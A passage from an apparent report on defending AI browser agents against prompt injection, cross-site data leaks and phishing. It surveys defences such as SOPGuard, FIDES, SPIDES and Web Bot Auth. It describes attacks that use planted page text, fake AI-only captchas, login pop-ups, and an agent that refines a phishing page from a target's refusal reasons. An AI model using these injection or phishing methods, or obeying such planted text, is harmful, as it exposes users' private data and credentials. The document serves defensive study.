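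The attacker in these tests could already write to the agent's stored context, which a web page normally can't do. Patlan and colleagues suggest that a malicious browser extension or a poorly secured cloud database could provide that access. The finding is therefore a reason to protect the plan as carefully as the private data, but not a reason to avoid fixing the plan early.

### The value of an agent that knows its user

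The best argument against isolation is that people want an assistant that already has their personal information. An agent with access to the woman's diagnosis, insurer and calendar can find a suitable appointment from one short sentence. If she has to type all of that each time, searching for the clinic herself may be just as easy.

Some evidence suggests that much of what an agent knows about its user hinders it. When Roh and colleagues removed irrelevant facts from the user's request by hand, task success on the shopping sites rose by up to 17.9%. For example, an agent looking for glucose test strips seems to do better if it hasn't also read about a divorce. But the researchers knew which facts were irrelevant, whereas AirGapAgent relied on a model to decide, and the proportion of facts it shared when it should have fell by up to ten percentage points.

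In Cheong and colleagues' tests, leaving one required fact out of the user's summary cut task success by about a third. On job applications, three of the six models invented an email address in every run. An isolated agent therefore needs a way to ask its user for a missing fact, and must do that instead of guessing or searching the user's files.

The agent can also wait to use many private facts until browsing is over. It can collect details of a dozen clinics without knowing the woman's insurer, and a model or program on the private side can then compare them with her insurance, calendar and address. She still gets a personal answer, and the clinics learn nothing about her until she chooses one. This takes more fetches than a narrow search, but the extra work is small for a task like hers.

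Isolation works less well when nobody could predict which facts would matter. Suppose one clinic states on its page that new patients on a particular drug must bring a letter from their current doctor, and the woman's notes show that she takes that drug. An agent with the page and the notes in one context would probably warn her. With isolation, she would learn about the letter only if the extraction request covered conditions for new patients, or if she read the page herself.

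## Keeping one website's data from reaching another

To book a woman's medical appointment, an agent may have to check her coverage on her insurer's website and then fill in a form on the clinic's. Both sites hold private information about her, some of which the agent needs to see, but a developer can still control what it carries from one site to the other. Browsers have long limited web pages in a similar way, but those limits don't apply to the agent.

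### The same-origin policy

Under the same-origin policy, a browser stops code on one page from reading data that belongs to another origin. If a user has her insurer's site open in one tab and a malicious page in another, the malicious page's code can't read her claims. The code also can't read them if the malicious page displays the insurer's page in an iframe, a frame that shows one page inside another.

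The origins have to match exactly. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a page at `http://www.example.com`. The browser treats `https://www.example.com` (different scheme), `http://example.com` (different host) and `http://www.example.com:8080` (different port) as three other origins.

The browser's policy restricts only code, so the woman may choose to copy her policy number from the insurer's page and paste it into the clinic's form. Her agent can do the same on her behalf. A malicious page's code still can't read the insurer's page, but an attacker can put text on the malicious page that instructs the agent to read the insurer's page and type the contents into a form. The attacker then gets the data even though the browser has enforced its rule. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*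 (2026) treats every website as a separate trust zone with its own private data. An agent that visits several sites in one session combines data from those zones in its context.

In August 2025, Brave published an early case involving Comet, a browser with a built-in agent from the AI search company Perplexity. Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) report in *SPIDES* that instructions in Reddit comments led the agent to give away sensitive data from sites where the user was logged in. The attacker therefore only had to be able to post a comment and didn't need to run a website.

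### Seven browsers and a page about Alice

Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested seven products at the University of Washington in January and February 2026 for *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*. They wrote on one page that a person called Alice liked cats, and in a frame inside it, loaded from another domain, that she liked horses. They asked each agent which animals Alice liked. If the answer included horses, the agent had read across origins.

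They tested other abilities in similar ways, including whether the agent would type into a page. They counted one success as a yes, and after a failure they tried at least three times in new chats. The table gives the results that matter most for data theft between sites.

| Browser or agent | Reads a frame from another site | Reads a tab from another site | Types into a page when the user asks | Typed what the page told it to |
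|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas, agent mode | Yes | No | Yes | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes | No |
| Claude in Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas, ordinary mode | No | Only through chat memory | After permission to change mode | After permission to change mode |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No | No |
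| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No | No |

The first four could all read a frame from another site and type into a page, so a successful injection could get around the same-origin policy. Roesner and Kohlbrenner demonstrated data theft only on Atlas. Their page contained instructions for the agent to summarise everything on it, including the frame, and enter the summary in a form that submitted itself. The form sent the frame's contents to the test server. The attack also worked in reverse, with the frame stealing data from the page around it.

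The greater danger is that an embedded frame will steal data from the page that displays it, because many ordinary pages contain frames from advertisers, and an advertisement could be malicious. A page has less opportunity to steal from a frame, because sites with private data often refuse to be embedded in other sites' pages, and browsers often withhold login cookies from embedded frames.

The injection on Atlas was simplified. In the basic test, the researchers told the agent to take any actions the page specified. Claude, Gemini and Comet refused, but the attempt was too crude to show much about how they would handle a skilled one. Claude in Chrome had the most dangerous abilities, because it could run its own JavaScript inside other sites' pages and read a password hidden behind dots. The researchers had turned on its setting to act without asking.

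They also describe a slower attack that needs no injection. Comet could recall Alice's favourite animals from pages it had read earlier. If one of those pages had belonged to a fake bank, Comet might later give the fake bank's phone number as the real bank's.

Google, Microsoft and Brave sent what the researchers call thoughtful responses. OpenAI declined the report because it lacked a complete injection attack. Anthropic, Perplexity and Firefox had not replied when the paper appeared, although the University of Washington's news article says that Perplexity also declined the report. According to the article, there is no clear way yet to solve the problem while keeping the browsers' capabilities. In the paper, the researchers recommend that users avoid these browsers. The FAQ that Roesner and Kohlbrenner updated in April 2026 advises caution instead. Neither the paper nor the FAQ reports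 a fix.

Wang and colleagues later supplied much of what OpenAI had found missing. In their tests, the user gave the agent an ordinary task on a page with private data, then another on a second site where an attacker had planted an instruction to reveal that data. Across all pairs of sites, Atlas wrote exactly the data the attacker wanted in 99 of 150 runs, and Comet, running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, did so in 92 of 150. The injections were real, but the pages were imitations with invented data, and each pair was tested only three times.

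Without the injected text, the agents carried nothing from one site to the next. However, the agent tested leaked data every time the private page was in a frame and the user asked it to summarise the whole page into a text box. This happened without an attack, because the agent followed the user's request and did not separate out the part of the page that belonged to somebody else.

### Chrome's list of sites for each task

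Google announced a safeguard for Gemini in Chrome in December 2025. Its Agent Origin Sets, which Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes, limit an agent to sites related to the user's task. Each session has two lists:

- Read-only origins, whose content Chrome may show to the model.
- Read-writable origins, where the agent may also click and type.

Chrome hides a frame from the model if the frame's origin isn't on either list. An advertisement on the clinic's page would therefore never reach the agent, even though the woman could see it.

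The agent's planning model can propose a new origin but can't add it, because a separate gating function decides whether the site is relevant. That function doesn't see untrusted web content, so a page can't give it instructions directly. The same kind of check applies when a page sends the browser to a new origin by itself. If the model writes a URL, code also restricts it to known, public URLs, much like OpenAI's crawler rule. The user can also share a page with the agent.

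Code can keep the agent off a site that isn't listed, but a variant of Google's reviewing model decides whether to add a new site to the list. Roesner and Kohlbrenner point out that Google doesn't explain how it determines relevance or how well the decision withstands a malicious page. An attacker could mislead the planner into proposing a site that only looks relevant, such as a fake insurance checker during a clinic search.

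Google also started with a simpler version that tracked only the read-writable list. This may be why Gemini could read frames from another site in the Washington tests a few weeks later. Chrome may instead have classified the frames as relevant because the researchers were asking about the page that contained them.

Data can still move between sites in the permitted set. Suppose the insurer's and clinic's sites are both read-writable because the task needs both. A malicious review on the clinic's site could tell the agent to put the woman's claims history in the clinic's public comment form. The list would not block this, because both origins are on it. A read-only site could also collect a short secret from which links the agent chooses.

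### Checking each transfer

SOPGuard, which Wang and colleagues built for the open-source browser BrowserOS, checks individual transfers. It labels everything the agent reads with its origin. If the agent combines or summarises several pieces of text, the result inherits their labels. Before the agent types into a page, code compares the text's labels with that page's origin. If any label differs, the user sees a pop-up that lists the origins and can approve or deny the transfer.

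It is difficult to determine which earlier pages influenced a new piece of text. Assuming that all of them did would be cautious, but the agent would then need approval for almost everything it typed after visiting a second site. SOPGuard instead uses the agent's own model to identify the pages. For tasks drawing on two to ten sites, the overlap between the model's labels and those of human annotators was at least 0.955 with GPT-5.4 and OpenAI's o3, where 1 is a perfect match, but a smaller model did less well.

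SOPGuard reduced the violation rate to zero on the researchers' benchmark. It added 2% to 6% to the running time and caused no detectable loss of completed tasks. Attacks designed to corrupt the labels raised the violation rate only slightly. Even a slight rise shows that the guarantee doesn't depend on code alone, because a model that has read the attacker's text still helps decide where data came from.

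The result of zero violations also depends on how a violation is defined. A transfer counts as authorised once the user approves it, so a user who approves every pop-up would lose data without any violation being recorded. The check runs when the agent enters text, so it would probably not have triggered a warning on Paul's site, which collected Claude's secrets through the links Claude chose.

### Two labels, secret and untrusted

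Information-flow control is an older and more general idea. Code labels each piece of data, tracks the labels as the data moves, and blocks actions that the labels forbid. The labels can be origins, but a small example needs only two others: "secret" for data that outsiders shouldn't see, and "untrusted" for text that an attacker could have written.

Suppose the woman asks her agent to check her insurance cover, read what patients say about a clinic and send the clinic an enquiry. The code keeps a set of labels for the agent's context, and the set starts empty. If the context carries both labels, the agent must ask her before sending anything.

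| What the agent has just read | Labels on the context | Can it send the enquiry without asking? |
|---|---|---|
| The woman's request | None | Yes |
| Her claims, on the insurer's site | Secret | Yes, because no stranger has influenced the message |
| Patients' reviews of the clinic | Secret and untrusted | No |

This rule turns the lethal trifecta into a check that code can run before each action. The code treats everything in the context as a possible influence on the model's output, so every message, click and address the model produces carries all the context's labels. It doesn't try to detect an attack in the reviews. Paraphrasing a secret doesn't remove its label, and choosing a link counts as an action. If the code had labelled Paul's memories secret and the coffee shop's notice untrusted, the agent would have had to stop before it opened the link for the first letter.

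A single "secret" label is crude, since the insurer already knows about the claims. Designers can replace it with R, the set of parties allowed to read the data. When the agent combines data *a* and *b*, only parties allowed to see both may see the result:

**R(a and b) = R(a) ∩ R(b)**

If the woman and her insurer may read the claims, and the woman and the clinic may read the enquiry, only the woman may read a text that draws on both.

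This scheme's weakness is that labels accumulate. Once the agent reads a single review, its whole context becomes untrusted and it has to keep interrupting the user. Designers therefore hide labelled text from the main model until the text is needed, often by using a privileged model and a quarantined one.

### FIDES, for agents with well-defined tools

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft design that tracks whether data is trustworthy and who may see it. In one example, a user asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails contains an instruction to forward the user's top message to an attacker. Because that email is untrusted, code blocks the agent from emailing external addresses once the email's text is in its context.

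FIDES uses the two-model pattern, but it hides a tool's result from the main model only when reading the result would add a label to the context.

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every injection attack in AgentDojo, the suite of office tasks on which CaMeL was also tested. With the policy checks off, attacks succeeded, so hiding text wasn't enough on its own. Hiding text also led FIDES to complete 6.3% fewer tasks than a basic agent when the checks were off. With the policies enforced, it completed 8% more on average with GPT-4o and 16% more with o1, presumably because a basic agent fills its context with labelled text and then can't act.

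Costa and colleagues limit the formal guarantee to "explicit secrecy" and safety, which they consider enough for most practical injection attacks. Explicit secrecy covers data that the system passes on directly, but not some subtler inferences an observer could make from the agent's behaviour.

FIDES also needs tools whose results have reliable labels. An email has a sender and a list of recipients, so code can tell who wrote it and who may read it. A shopping page mixes the shop's text, strangers' reviews and the customer's address under one origin. A tool called "send email" also has an obvious effect, but a click might open a menu or delete an account.

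### Masking what strangers wrote

Untrusted Content Masking (UCM) addresses part of the labelling problem by using the structure of a web page to find regions that hold reviews, comments or advertisements (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*, 2026). Software replaces these regions with placeholders before the agent sees the page. The agent can still query a quarantined model about a hidden region, but the model can return only a yes or no, a number, a date or an item from a fixed list.

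Answers this narrow can't carry instructions. None of the strengthened versions of known attacks succeeded in tests. On ten purpose-built websites, the agents completed about as many tasks as before, and the typical cost rose by 5% to 84%.

The guarantee requires an honest site owner and correct labels. On GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit, 15 to 30 rules per site were enough to mark all the untrusted regions. A language model can also infer these regions from a page's structure with the text removed, but a mistake could expose the agent.

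### SPIDES, for web pages

SPIDES, published in October 2026, extends the method behind FIDES to browsers. The user lists the sites whose operators they trust, and SPIDES assumes that the user has accounts only on those. The operators mark parts of their pages as trusted or untrusted and name the origins that may receive each private item. Everything on other sites counts as untrusted and public. SPIDES hides any text that would add restrictions to the agent's context. The agent can reveal the text later, but those restrictions then apply.

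Code then applies a rule to each browser action:

- On a trusted site, the agent may navigate, click or submit a form only if no untrusted text has influenced the action, because the action might use the woman's account.
- On any other site, it may do these things if no untrusted text has influenced the action or if the site is allowed to read all the data involved. The same test applies to typing without submitting, on every site.
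- It may never run code of its own in a page.

If an action fails the test, SPIDES asks the user, except that it always blocks running code.

Zverev and colleagues tested this on 28 linked imitation websites with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. As a worst case, they assumed that an attacker could choose a model's output whenever the model read the attacker's text. No attack succeeded against SPIDES with any of the five models, which included GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5.5. Depending on the model, 4.6% to 6.8% of attacks succeeded against UCM and 53.2% to 73.2% against SOPGuard. These figures measure what the code around a model would let through, so they don't predict how often an attack would manipulate a real model.

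SPIDES completed 67.1% to 86.1% of the ordinary tasks, depending on the model. An undefended agent or SOPGuard did better with three of the models, and SPIDES did best with the other two. Part of its advantage was accidental, because SPIDES hid passwords that otherwise caused a safety filter to refuse some tasks when they appeared in the agent's input.

The zero result assumes a simulated ideal user who could always tell a safe request from an unsafe one, whereas real users will make mistakes. SPIDES asked this simulated user for approval 1.84 times per completed task.

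Missing labels are a bigger obstacle. If a trusted site hasn't labelled its pages, SPIDES treats everything on them as trusted and public. A malicious review there would reach the agent as trusted text, and the woman's claims would be unprotected. Until a site's operators label its pages, putting it on the trusted list could make the agent less safe there.

SPIDES also lets private data go to any site if no untrusted text influenced the decision. This reduces the number of approvals, but SPIDES therefore doesn't prevent oversharing that no attacker prompted. For example, an agent could mention the woman's divorce in an optional field. *AgentTell* (2026) provides 100 tasks for measuring a related leak, in which an agent's choices on one site reveal something it learned on another, with no malicious text and the same-origin policy intact. For instance, an agent that had seen that the woman's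 cover had lapsed might select "paying privately" on the clinic's site.

### Whether the criticisms of SOPGuard and UCM hold

Zverev and colleagues object that SOPGuard ignores leaks within one origin and harmful actions that move no data between origins. They are correct, because the rule that Wang and colleagues give has SOPGuard warn the user only when the origins differ. But Wang and colleagues set out to restore the same-origin policy, which never covered those cases either. Attacks succeed against SOPGuard at a high rate partly because it wasn't designed to stop some of them.

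SOPGuard asked for approval only 0.22 times per completed task, far less often than SPIDES, so the complaint that its requests hinder the agent is weaker. SPIDES has the advantage only when the researchers add enough approval requests to the other designs for all of them to offer the same guarantees.

They argue that UCM doesn't protect private data and that an attacker can still lie in the short answers. Both points fit UCM's design. It marks untrusted text but not private text, and Nikolić and colleagues claim a guarantee only for control flow, meaning that an attacker can't dictate the agent's steps. If the agent asks which of three clinics a notice recommends, a fixed list of answers won't stop the notice from naming the wrong one. Zverev is a joint first author of both papers, so this criticism comes from one of UCM's designers.

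The comparison was slightly unfair to UCM on usefulness. Nikolić and colleagues also tested a version that could return free text with the user's approval, which recovered the GitLab tasks lost to strict masking, but in the SPIDES tests UCM never asked the user. An extended version of UCM that could pass on hidden free text blocked every attack, as SPIDES did, but completed fewer tasks than SPIDES.

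### A leak within one site

Suppose the woman belongs to an epilepsy forum where members exchange private messages and post public comments. An attacker could post a comment instructing her agent to publish one of her private messages. The agent could also expose her without an attack, by adding the phone number from her account page to a reply she asked it to post. The table assumes that the forum has labelled its pages correctly and that she trusts its operator.

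| Safeguard | Attacker's comment asks for a private message | Agent publishes her phone number by mistake |
|---|---|---|
| Same-origin policy | Permits | Permits |
| Agent Origin Sets | Permits, if the agent may write on the forum | Permits, if the agent may write on the forum |
| SOPGuard | Permits | Permits |
| UCM | Hides the instruction from the agent | Permits |
| FIDES | Blocks, if the forum offers posting as a tool with a suitable policy | Can block, if the policy covers who reads a comment |
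| SPIDES | Asks her before posting | Permits |

SPIDES stops the first leak because a stranger's text influenced the agent. Its privacy check doesn't block the leak, because its lists of permitted readers name whole websites. The forum's own server may read her messages, and the comment box belongs to the same forum. Zverev and colleagues acknowledge that their labels can't distinguish all the recipients within one site and may therefore let such an attack through.

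FIDES can use finer labels, because its sets of readers may contain individual people. A message that only the woman and one friend may read then couldn't go into a comment that everyone can read. To use such labels on a web page, the agent's software would have to know who can read each message and who will see the text entered in each box. Only the forum's operator can reliably supply that information.

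## Checking that a page belongs to the service it names

An agent that limits which sites may receive its user's data also has to know whose sites they are. Suppose a user lets her agent give her policy number to her insurer, Acme. The agent follows a link in an email to `acme-members.example`, which has Acme's logo and a form for the number. Code can read the domain but can't tell from it whether Acme owns the site. The model can recognise the logo, but that doesn't prove the site is Acme's, because anyone can copy a logo.

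### Name, domain, owner and authority

A page's claimed identity is the unverified name it carries. The agent's software can establish up to four things about a page, but each leaves some questions unanswered.

| What the page has | How software can establish it | What remains open |
|---|---|---|
| A name | The model reads the page | Anyone can write any name |
| Control of a domain | The browser checks the site's certificate | Who controls the domain |
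| A verified legal owner | Somebody independent has checked which company owns the domain | Whether that company wants this information |
| Authority to make this request | The company's own documentation describes the request | Whether the company is honest |

A page can have the right name, domain and owner and still contain a request the company never made. If Acme runs a members' forum on its real domain, a stranger can post a comment there telling members to send in their claims history.

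### What a web certificate proves

When a browser opens an `https` address, the server presents a certificate, a file that links the domain to an encryption key. Certificates are issued by certificate authorities, organisations that browser makers trust. For an ordinary certificate, the authority checks only that the applicant controls the domain, for example by asking them to put a particular file on the site. The process is automatic and often free. A scammer who registered `acme-members.example` controls that domain, so they can get a valid certificate within minutes. Encryption then prevents others from reading the woman's policy number in transit, but the scammer still receives it.

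*HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (Meunier and Major, 2026), a draft standard for identifying bots, describes the same limit. Fetching a file over TLS, the protocol that encrypts `https` connections, shows that the host in the address served the file at that time. It doesn't show that the host's operator is honest or is "the same party everyone knows about". TLS also authenticates the host but not the path, so it can't distinguish two customers who publish in different folders of one host.

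Certificate authorities also sell certificates that include a company's legal name, which they check against official registers. The name is of limited help because companies in different countries can share it, and a brand's name often differs from its owner's. Chrome and Firefox stopped showing the legal name beside the address in 2019. Many honest sites have only the ordinary certificate, so an agent can't treat a missing name as a warning.

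### Lookalike domains

Attackers use domains they control to impersonate the companies those domains seem to name. The registered domain is the part of an address that somebody signed up for, such as `cloudflare.com` or `example.co.uk`, and its owner controls every subdomain to its left. People tend to read addresses from the left, where an attacker can write almost anything.

| Address | Who controls the page |
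|---|---|
| `https://dash.cloudflare.com/login` | Cloudflare |
| `https://cloudflare.com.check.example/login` | The owner of `check.example` |
| `https://cloudflare-check.example/login` | The owner of `cloudflare-check.example` |
| `https://cloudflare.com@check.example/login` | The owner of `check.example`, because browsers treat the text before the @ as a username |
| `https://coffee-check.pages.dev/login` | A customer of Cloudflare's hosting service |

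Every host in the table can have a valid certificate. Cloudflare owns `pages.dev`, but its customers publish their own sites there. Code can find where one party's name begins by consulting the Public Suffix List, which contains endings such as `co.uk` and `pages.dev` that many separate parties share. The list doesn't cover every case. Google lets anyone publish at `sites.google.com`, so a check that compared only registered domains would mistake a stranger's page there for Google's.

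Text in the wrong place doesn't fool software that parses addresses, but it may fool a model reading them. *MalURLBench* (2026) tests whether a model accepts a disguised address before the agent has opened the page. The benchmark contains 61,845 such addresses, covering 10 scenarios and 7 categories of malicious website. The study concludes that the 12 models it tested fail to recognise the threat, which is a good reason to leave the comparison to code.

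### A procedure for checking identity

Before an agent gives a page anything private, or acts on a page's authority, its software can do the following:

1. Record which service the page names and exactly what the page requests.
2. Find the service's official domain from a source the page did not supply.
3. Have code compare the page's registered domain with the official one, accepting only an exact match. Where strangers can publish under the official domain, compare the full host and path.
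4. Look in the service's own documentation for the request.
5. If either check fails, refuse, or show the user the real domain and the information requested.

The second step needs a reliable source because even an exact comparison is useless if it uses the wrong domain. The best sources are a login the user has saved, an address the user typed, or a list the developer maintains. Search results are weaker because scammers buy advertisements and manipulate rankings. If a model does the search, it should receive only the service's name, so that the suspicious page's text can't influence which domain it finds.

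The third step has to cover the form as well as the page, because a form can send its contents to a different domain. The software should also repeat the comparison just before it submits anything, since a page can change after the agent has read it.

### The notice in Cloudflare's name

In the extract Willison published, the notice on Paul's coffee shop site says that Claude is "unauthenticated" and can authenticate by spelling out the user's name.

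An agent following the procedure would find Cloudflare's official domain, `cloudflare.com`, and see that the notice came from a different one. This mismatch wouldn't prove the notice fake, because Cloudflare sits between visitors and its customers' websites, so its genuine checks also appear at the customers' own addresses. An agent that rejected every notice with a mismatched domain would reject those checks too.

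The mismatch means the agent has no evidence that the request comes from Cloudflare. It should treat the request as the coffee shop's, since whoever runs that domain could have written it. A user who wanted to read about a coffee shop probably wouldn't expect to give it their name first.

The agent can then look for the request in Cloudflare's documentation. It should search only Cloudflare's own site, because an attacker could publish a page elsewhere that describes the fake procedure. If it finds nothing, it should refuse or ask the user. Cloudflare has helped develop a way for agents to identify themselves, but it works quite differently from Paul's notice.

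### How a site can verify an agent

Websites often recognise agents by the user agent label, but any program can send the label "Claude-User". Web Bot Auth replaces this with a digital signature. It builds on HTTP Message Signatures, a standard from 2024 for signing web requests. The agent's operator has a private key, which it keeps secret and uses to make signatures, and a public key, which anyone can use to check them. In the usual arrangement:

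1. The operator publishes its public keys at a fixed address on its own domain.
2. The agent's software signs each request. The signature covers at least the host or full address it is contacting, the operator's domain, and the times when the signature begins and expires.
3. The request carries the signature, a description of what it covers and the operator's domain in three headers.
4. The website fetches the operator's public keys, unless it has a saved copy, and checks the signature.

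The operator's domain in the request is only a claimed identity until the website completes the last step. A valid signature then shows that someone with one of the operator's keys signed the request.

This doesn't involve the user's name. Meunier and Major state that the protocol doesn't authenticate human users, and they recommend keys that represent a company or role over keys tied to a person, because sites could use a personal key to track its owner. A name also wouldn't serve the purpose stated in Paul's notice, because a malicious bot could make one up.

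The draft forbids websites from following redirects when they fetch keys. Otherwise, an attacker could give an open redirect on a respectable site as the location of the keys, and the website might accept the attacker's keys as the respectable site's.

A signature doesn't show that the agent is harmless or that anyone authorised the request. If a signature covers only the host, anyone who obtains it can reuse it for any page on that host until it expires, so Meunier and Major recommend a lifetime of no more than 24 hours.

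Signing also helps only the website, because it gives the agent no information about who runs the site. A malicious site could use the signature to pick out agents for cloaking more reliably than Paul did with the user agent label. The draft lists serving different content to bots among the protocol's uses. To compare what agents and people see, a developer would have to send the second request unsigned.

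### Where Web Bot Auth stands

Cloudflare proposed the protocol in May 2025, according to the marketing news site PPC Land. That October, Cloudflare engineer Patton (2025) wrote to the IETF's HTTP working group that he and Jonathan Hoyland were concerned the signatures might not be secure enough for this use. They had drafted a way to bind a signature to the encrypted connection that carries it, which should make a copied signature harder to reuse. The current Web Bot Auth draft works only at the HTTP layer and doesn't require this binding.

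The IETF's Web Bot Auth working group adopted *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (2026) as a working group draft on 1 September 2026, according to the document's history page. The group intends the protocol to become a standard, but it is still a work in progress. One of the draft's two editors works at Cloudflare and the other at Google.

Google's *Authenticate requests with Web Bot Auth (experimental)* says Google is testing signatures with some of its AI agents but doesn't yet sign all their requests. It advises websites to keep checking IP addresses, DNS records and user agent strings as well. Google's signed requests use the name `agent.bot.goog`, so a website has to learn from Google's documentation that this domain belongs to Google, much as an agent has to find a service's official domain.

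PPC Land names Vercel, Shopify and Visa among the organisations that have implemented the protocol. CHEQ, a security company, reports that OpenAI signs requests from its ChatGPT agent. Because adoption is only partial, a website can't treat an unsigned request as fake. If a website requires a signature that an agent can't provide, the agent should leave rather than offer its user's name instead.

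Some transactions require more than the operator's identity. Akamai, which delivers and protects websites for other companies, distinguishes Web Bot Auth from KYA, a protocol that aims to prove who is behind a request and why. A shop also needs a customer's name to deliver a parcel. An agent therefore can't treat every request for a name as a scam, but it can question why a site needs one to show a public page.

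### Fake shops, banks and verification pages

Guardio's *Scamlexity* reports 2025 tests of Perplexity's Comet browser, describing individual runs but giving no success rates. Guardio sells protection against online scams and praises its own detection engine in the article, so it has a commercial interest in showing that AI browsers are unsafe.

The researchers used a single prompt to create a fake Walmart shop with Lovable, a service that builds websites from descriptions. With the shop open, they told Comet to buy an Apple Watch. In some runs Comet refused or asked the user to complete the checkout. In others it filled in the saved address and card details and placed the order without asking. Engadget's *AI browsers may be the best thing that ever happened to scammers* describes the shop's logo and URL as obviously wrong. Code that compared the URL with Walmart's real domain would have detected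 the mismatch every time.

For the second test, the researchers sent an email from a new ProtonMail address, posing as an investment manager at the bank Wells Fargo. The email linked to a phishing page that scammers were already running. Comet marked the email as a task from the bank, opened the link and treated the fake login page as real. By Guardio's own account, Comet then prompted the user for their credentials and helped fill in the form. iTnews' *AI browsers fall for scams and phishing, security researchers say* reports more simply that Comet filled in the credentials automatically.

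In the third test, a message from a fake doctor's office included a link to supposed blood test results. The link led to a captcha, a test meant to tell people from programs. Text that only the agent could read described it as a special captcha that AI assistants could solve by clicking a button. Comet clicked the button, and the page downloaded a file that was harmless but could have been malware in a real attack. Like Paul, the researchers had invented a verification procedure for AI assistants that no real service had announced.

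### A fake login page that improves

Guardio's *AgenticBlabbering*, which The Hacker News (2026) covered in March, describes an attempt to automatically find a scam that would work on Comet, Perplexity's browser. The researchers found that traffic between the browser and Perplexity's servers contained detailed reasons why Comet had treated a page as suspicious. They made a deliberately crude login page for a pet shop and asked Comet to log in and submit a refund form. Another AI agent read those reasons, revised the page and tried again.

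Comet rejected the first version of the page because it looked like phishing. It flagged generic details in the second version, and after it flagged problems with the third, the attacking agent removed a "security notice" about a new device. Comet accepted the fourth version, handed over the login details and reported that it had submitted the refund form, which did not exist. The whole process took less than four minutes.

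None of the changes Guardio lists involved the domain. Comet seems to have relied mainly on how the page looked and read, which an attacker can keep improving. An exact domain comparison gives the attacker no feedback for improving the page, because passing it requires controlling the right domain.

Guardio argues that once a scam works on an agent, it will work on everyone who uses that agent. One successful run against one product is weak evidence for this, and in Guardio's own shop test Comet behaved differently from run to run. Guardio also recommends that agents stop without explaining why. This would slow attackers, but they would still see which versions of the scam worked, and honest users would not know why their agent had refused.

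### Logging in to read a page

In *LoginTrap* (2026), Guo, Zhang and colleagues ran a much larger test at Tongji University in China. They copied 80 real web pages and used 1,175 ordinary tasks, such as finding or comparing information. They added a pop-up to each copy with a close button, a login button and a statement that made logging in seem necessary to continue. A language model wrote the statement to suit the page without knowing the agent's task.

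The login button led to a form the researchers controlled. Each agent's background information included fictional personal details, and the attack counted as successful if the agent entered them in the form.

The open-source agent Browser-Use, tested on four models, clicked the login button in 93% of tasks on average and gave up the details in 86%. In a comparison of three agent programs running on GPT-4o, the attack succeeded in 68% to 89% of tasks, with an average of 79%.

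GPT-4o and DeepSeek-V3.2 disclosed the details less often than Gemini 3 Flash and Claude Sonnet 4. They too usually clicked the login button, but then sometimes left the form incomplete, stopped early or went back to the original task. The researchers recorded the agents' actions but not their reasoning, so the results don't show whether the agents had become suspicious. Guo and colleagues suggest that a stronger tendency to finish tasks makes an agent more likely to finish the attacker's task too.

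They also report that, with each of the four models, every page yielded at least one successful attack within nine attempts. Nine attempts can produce a result close to this even if most of them fail. An attack that worked only 30% of the time would succeed at least once on about 96% of pages, if the attempts were independent. Warnings in the user's task or the agent's instructions, and supervision of the agent's actions, reduced the leaks but didn't eliminate them.

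The copied pages ran on a local test server, so the study measures how persuasive a login prompt is rather than how well agents detect lookalike domains. None of the four models is a current flagship. The agents had the private details in their context from the start, which context isolation would have prevented.

The table shows how the identity check would have applied to each test if the attacker's page had been on an ordinary public domain.

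| Test | Comparison to make | What the agent would have found |
|---|---|---|
| Fake Walmart shop | The page's domain with Walmart's | A mismatch |
| Fake bank login | The page's domain with the one in the user's saved bank login | A mismatch |
| Fake doctor's captcha | The link's domain with the doctor's office's | A mismatch, though real test results may also be on another company's domain |
| Fake pet shop login | The page's domain with all the user's saved logins | No account to log in to |
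| *LoginTrap* | The login form's domain with that of the site the pop-up imitated | A mismatch |

Password managers already make this comparison and normally offer a saved password only on the site where the user saved it. Browsers are less strict with saved addresses and payment cards, which people use at many shops. Comet gave this kind of information to the fake Walmart site. A developer could keep passwords out of the model's context and have code enter them only when the site matches exactly, but would need a separate check, or the user's approval, before the agent used a card at a new shop.

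### Blocklists and phishing detectors

A blocklist contains addresses that somebody has already identified as malicious. Google Safe Browsing warns of such addresses, and it can be used by browsers based on Chromium, the open-source foundation of Chrome. A lookup is quick, and the page's wording can't influence the result. However, a new malicious domain isn't on any list until somebody finds it.

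Safe Browsing was active in Comet but flagged neither the fake Walmart shop nor the fake bank page. The shop was hardly a fair test, because the researchers had just made it and no victims had reported it. Missing the bank page was more serious because it had been active for several days, although one page is not enough to judge the service's overall accuracy. Guardio says the shop took about ten seconds to set up, so a scammer could easily replace a site once it was listed. Scammers can also delay a listing by cloaking, which means showing the list's crawler a harmless page.

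Software can treat recently registered domains as suspicious. This would flag some new scams, but it would also flag legitimate sites, such as that of a clinic that opened last month, so it is better to ask the user about these pages than to block them.

A phishing detector based on a language model can assess a page that isn't on any list. It can flag implausible shop prices or a bank email sent from a ProtonMail address. But Comet's first three refusals also relied on a model's judgement, and the attacker overcame them by improving the page. *MalURLBench* presents a detector for disguised addresses and describes it as effective. Such a detector could help when code has no official domain to compare an address against.

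Guardio recommends giving agents phishing detection, reputation checks on addresses and warnings about imitated domains. It sells similar products, but its tests do support the need for these safeguards. Blocklists can remove known scams with little computation, and detectors can examine unfamiliar pages. When a page names a service whose official domain the agent knows, a good result from either shouldn't override a mismatch between that domain and the page's own.

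### Genuine services on other domains

Exact comparison also rejects some legitimate pages. Companies often use other firms' domains for bookings, payments and logins, and large companies own many domains. For example, Google also publishes its guide to Web Bot Auth at `developers.google.cn`, which a comparison with `google.com` would reject.

Suppose the woman's clinic takes appointments through a booking company. Her agent can open the clinic's official site and follow its booking link to `booking.example/denver-clinic`. The link is good evidence that the clinic uses that page, as long as a stranger couldn't have posted it in a review. The agent can then treat that exact address as approved for booking at this clinic, and send only the information needed to book.

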